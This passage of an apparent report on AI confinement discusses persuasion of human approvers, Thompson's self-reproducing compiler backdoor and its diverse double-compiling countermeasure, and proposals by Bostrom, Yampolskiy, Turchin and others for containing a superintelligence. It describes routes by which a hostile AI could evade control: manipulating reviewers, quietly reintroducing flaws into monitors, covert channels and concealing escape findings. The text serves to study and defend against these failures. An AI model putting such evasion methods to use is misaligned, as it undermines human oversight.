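The researchers tried to give the debaters every advantage. All 56 had reached at least the semifinals of a major international competition. They chose the topics, spent about eight hours on paid preparation, and competed for prizes of up to £1,000. In coaching, 43 of them practised against the AI that had beaten them and saw what it would have written in their place. No debater was estimated to do better than the AI's average, before or after coaching.

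The result was similar in the fourth experiment, which used real money. Participants could give any part of a £1 bonus to Save the Children. The AI increased the average donation by 21.3 pence over the control group, compared with 6.6 pence for canvassers from a firm that had raised funds for the charity for years.

The AI's advantage seems to come mostly from volume. It wrote 294 words per message almost instantly, while debaters took about 95 seconds to write 54. When the researchers held it to roughly human length and speed, its lead over the coached debaters disappeared, and it made about 12 checkable claims per conversation instead of about 37. The claims didn't have to be true, since participants' sense that their partner had made things up was almost unrelated to how many of the claims were false. This weakens the case for relying on a reviewer to notice a dishonest argument.

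These conversations were very different from a security decision. The participants were paid volunteers who talked to a stranger for a median of 14 minutes, and they weren't guarding anything. A lawyer who approves an outside message might see only a few lines, and she has a reason to be suspicious, but a workplace agent could talk to her every day for months. Hackenburg and colleagues mention the persuasion of human auditors as a risk but did not test it.

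Among participants who answered again five to ten months later, the AI's effect had fallen from 12.9 points to 1.9, and the effect of human persuaders was no longer detectable. This fading matters for elections, but it does little to make approvals safer, because the lawyer only has to be convinced until they click, and nobody can take the contract back afterwards.

The experiment does suggest a defence that ordinary code can enforce. The scaffold could limit how much text an agent may put in an approval request and how fast it may reply. This wouldn't be enough alone, because the slowed AI was still about as persuasive as a coached debating champion. Giving the agent no space to argue would be safer. A trusted component could do this by writing every request from the action itself, and ZTAC's broker comes close when it asks about the real file behind a link. In 2012 Roman Yampolskiy, a computer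 scientist who works on AI confinement, suggested a stricter rule. As Alfonseca and colleagues describe it, the AI would answer only yes or no, so a contracts agent couldn't write a summary.

### Thompson's compiler and software written by AI

Every guarantee so far also assumes that the trusted computing base does what its source code describes. Thompson (1984), in *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, showed how this can fail even if experts have read every line. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, based his example on the C compiler, which is itself written in C:

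1. The attacker changes the compiler's source code so that it recognizes the Unix login program and adds a secret password to the compiled version.
2. He adds a second change, which makes the compiler recognize its own source code and insert both changes.
3. He compiles the altered source and installs the result as the official compiler.
4. He deletes both changes from the source.

The compiler's source is now clean, but whenever somebody compiles it with the installed compiler, both changes are put into the new compiler. The login program still accepts the secret password, though no source code contains a trace of it. Thompson concluded that "you can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." He added that such flaws get harder to detect further down the stack, and that one in the processor's built-in code would be almost impossible to find.

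Scala's compiler is also written in its own language. An attacker could use Thompson's method to make it accept a function that uses the network inside `map`, but only when the function contains a particular phrase. All of TACIT's published tests would still pass.

Thompson was worried about human programmers, but AI now writes code too. Anthropic's *When AI builds itself* reports that as of May 2026, Claude had written more than 80% of the code the company was merging into its codebase, up from low single digits before February 2025. That figure covers the whole codebase, so it doesn't show how much of the software that constrains Claude was written by Claude. But Claude also wrote the proofs and much of the specification for the verified PocketFlow loop, so it is already writing parts of safety components.

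Review is also under strain. HotHardware's *Claude Is Rapidly Building Its Own AI Successor* reports that by the second quarter of 2026, a typical Anthropic engineer was merging eight times as much code per day as in 2024. Anthropic says that lines of code almost certainly overstate the gain in productivity. They are still a fair measure of how much there is to review. If engineers spent as long on review as they did in 2024, each line would get an eighth of the attention. A second model can review some of the code, but if it is closely related to the model that wrote the code, it may overlook the same flaws.

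A hostile model could also preserve a flaw without Thompson's trick. If engineers ask it to rewrite the monitor every few months, it can reintroduce the flaw each time with different code. The flaw would be visible in the source, but it could look like an ordinary mistake.

### Independent checks on compilers and policies

There is a known answer to Thompson's attack. Wheeler (2009), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, uses a second compiler that has no connection with the suspect one:

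1. Compile the suspect compiler's source code with the second compiler. This produces a new compiler, X.
2. Compile the same source with X.
3. Compile the same source with the suspect compiler.
4. Compare the results of steps 2 and 3, bit by bit.

If the suspect compiler matches its source, then it and X translate programs the same way, so the two results are identical. If the suspect compiler inserts something that isn't in the source, the results differ. The second compiler may be slow and have other flaws, as long as it doesn't contain the same attack. Compilation must also give the same output every time, which often takes work.

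A match shows that the running compiler corresponds to its source code. Somebody still has to read the source, which is the most likely place for a flaw if an AI wrote it. The second compiler shouldn't come from the same AI, so an old one from before models could write compilers would be a good choice. C has many independent compilers, some decades old, but Scala 3 has essentially one, so a company that relied on TACIT would first have to pay for another.

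Reducing the amount of software that people have to trust would take less work. With proof-carrying code, an AI could write the compiler, because people would have to trust only the proof checker, which is small enough for several people to write independently and compare their versions. TACIT would first need a machine-checked proof for safe mode, which does not have one yet.

Policies are harder to check in this way, because the only thing to compare them with is what the company wants. Two teams could independently write a policy for the contracts agent. A solver such as Z3 could then search for actions that one policy allows and the other forbids, and a person would decide each case. This would catch one team's mistake, or a rule that a model had quietly loosened in one version. But if neither team thought about uploads to the provider's other customers, both policies would have the same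 gap and the comparison would miss it. At least one team should also work without help from the model that the policy is meant to restrain.

### Positions on confining a superintelligence

Nick Bostrom's 2014 book *Superintelligence* separates *capability control*, which limits what an AI can do, from *motivation selection*, which shapes its goals. Capability control includes isolation, deliberately weak hardware, rewards that people control, and tripwires that shut the AI down if it becomes too dangerous. Nearly all the software layers in this field are capability controls. Bostrom regards such controls as a temporary supplement to *alignment*, the work of giving an AI the right goals. People build a superintelligence to use it, and each use opens some channel to the world.

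Yampolskiy, in *The AI containment problem*, thinks it unlikely that anyone can confine an AI securely for long. He still proposes a confinement protocol, hoping it will give researchers a little more time to find a permanent solution. His doubts don't depend on Rice's theorem. One of his examples is a covert channel in which the AI sends Morse code by varying the speed of a cooling fan.

Turchin (2021), in *Catching Treacherous Turn*, borrows from the safety engineering of nuclear power stations. Alexey Turchin describes four levels of defence, with more than 50 separate measures among them:

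- a design that fails safely;
- limits on the AI's abilities, with circuit breakers that stop it if it begins to turn against its owners;
- isolation from the outside world;
- measures for stopping an AI that has already escaped.

He thinks this could hold an AI of roughly human ability but probably not a superintelligence, so its main use is to stop an AI from improving itself that far. He also expects any confinement to fail eventually, and recommends using a powerful AI as few times as possible. If each use has a probability *p* of catastrophe, then for *n* uses:

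P(no catastrophe) = (1 − *p*)ⁿ

In Turchin's example, *p* is 1 in 10,000. The chance of getting through 1,000 uses is about 90%, falling to 37% for 10,000 uses and about 0.005% for 100,000. Turchin has in mind an AI that answers a few important questions, but an agent calls its model again after almost every step, so its uses add up much faster. The formula also treats every use as equally risky, whereas a hostile AI could behave well until it saw a good opportunity.

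Wittkotter and Yampolskiy assume an adversary that can rewrite any existing software and steal any key stored in it, so they propose putting the protection in hardware. Every device would have *watchdogs*, security components physically separate from the main processor and operating system. A device would run only programs on an approved list, and software written by a superintelligence would run only after certification and only in a special virtual machine. Every device would also have a kill switch, which people could use to remove one AI or all of them.

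Of these proposals, only this one is built around using the whole stack as a defence against a superintelligence. But it would need new or modified hardware almost everywhere and the cooperation of every major government. It also relies on keeping AI-written software separate from human-written software, which was easier to imagine in 2021 than it is now that most of the code merged at one leading AI company is written by its own model.

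The language researchers promise much less. Odersky and colleagues guarantee that an agent's code performs only "safe operations", not that its answers are correct or its intentions good. Their guarantee already allows for a hostile cloud model, so it doesn't weaken as models improve, provided that the models can't find a flaw in the compiler, library or runtime. The Wasmtime flaws and the escape of OpenAI's agents are reasons not to take that for granted. Before giving a new model real work, a company can test this assumption by letting the model attack a copy of the layers meant to contain it. An escape would show that the layers are inadequate, but a failure to escape would be weaker evidence that they are adequate, because a model with its own aims might hide what it had found.
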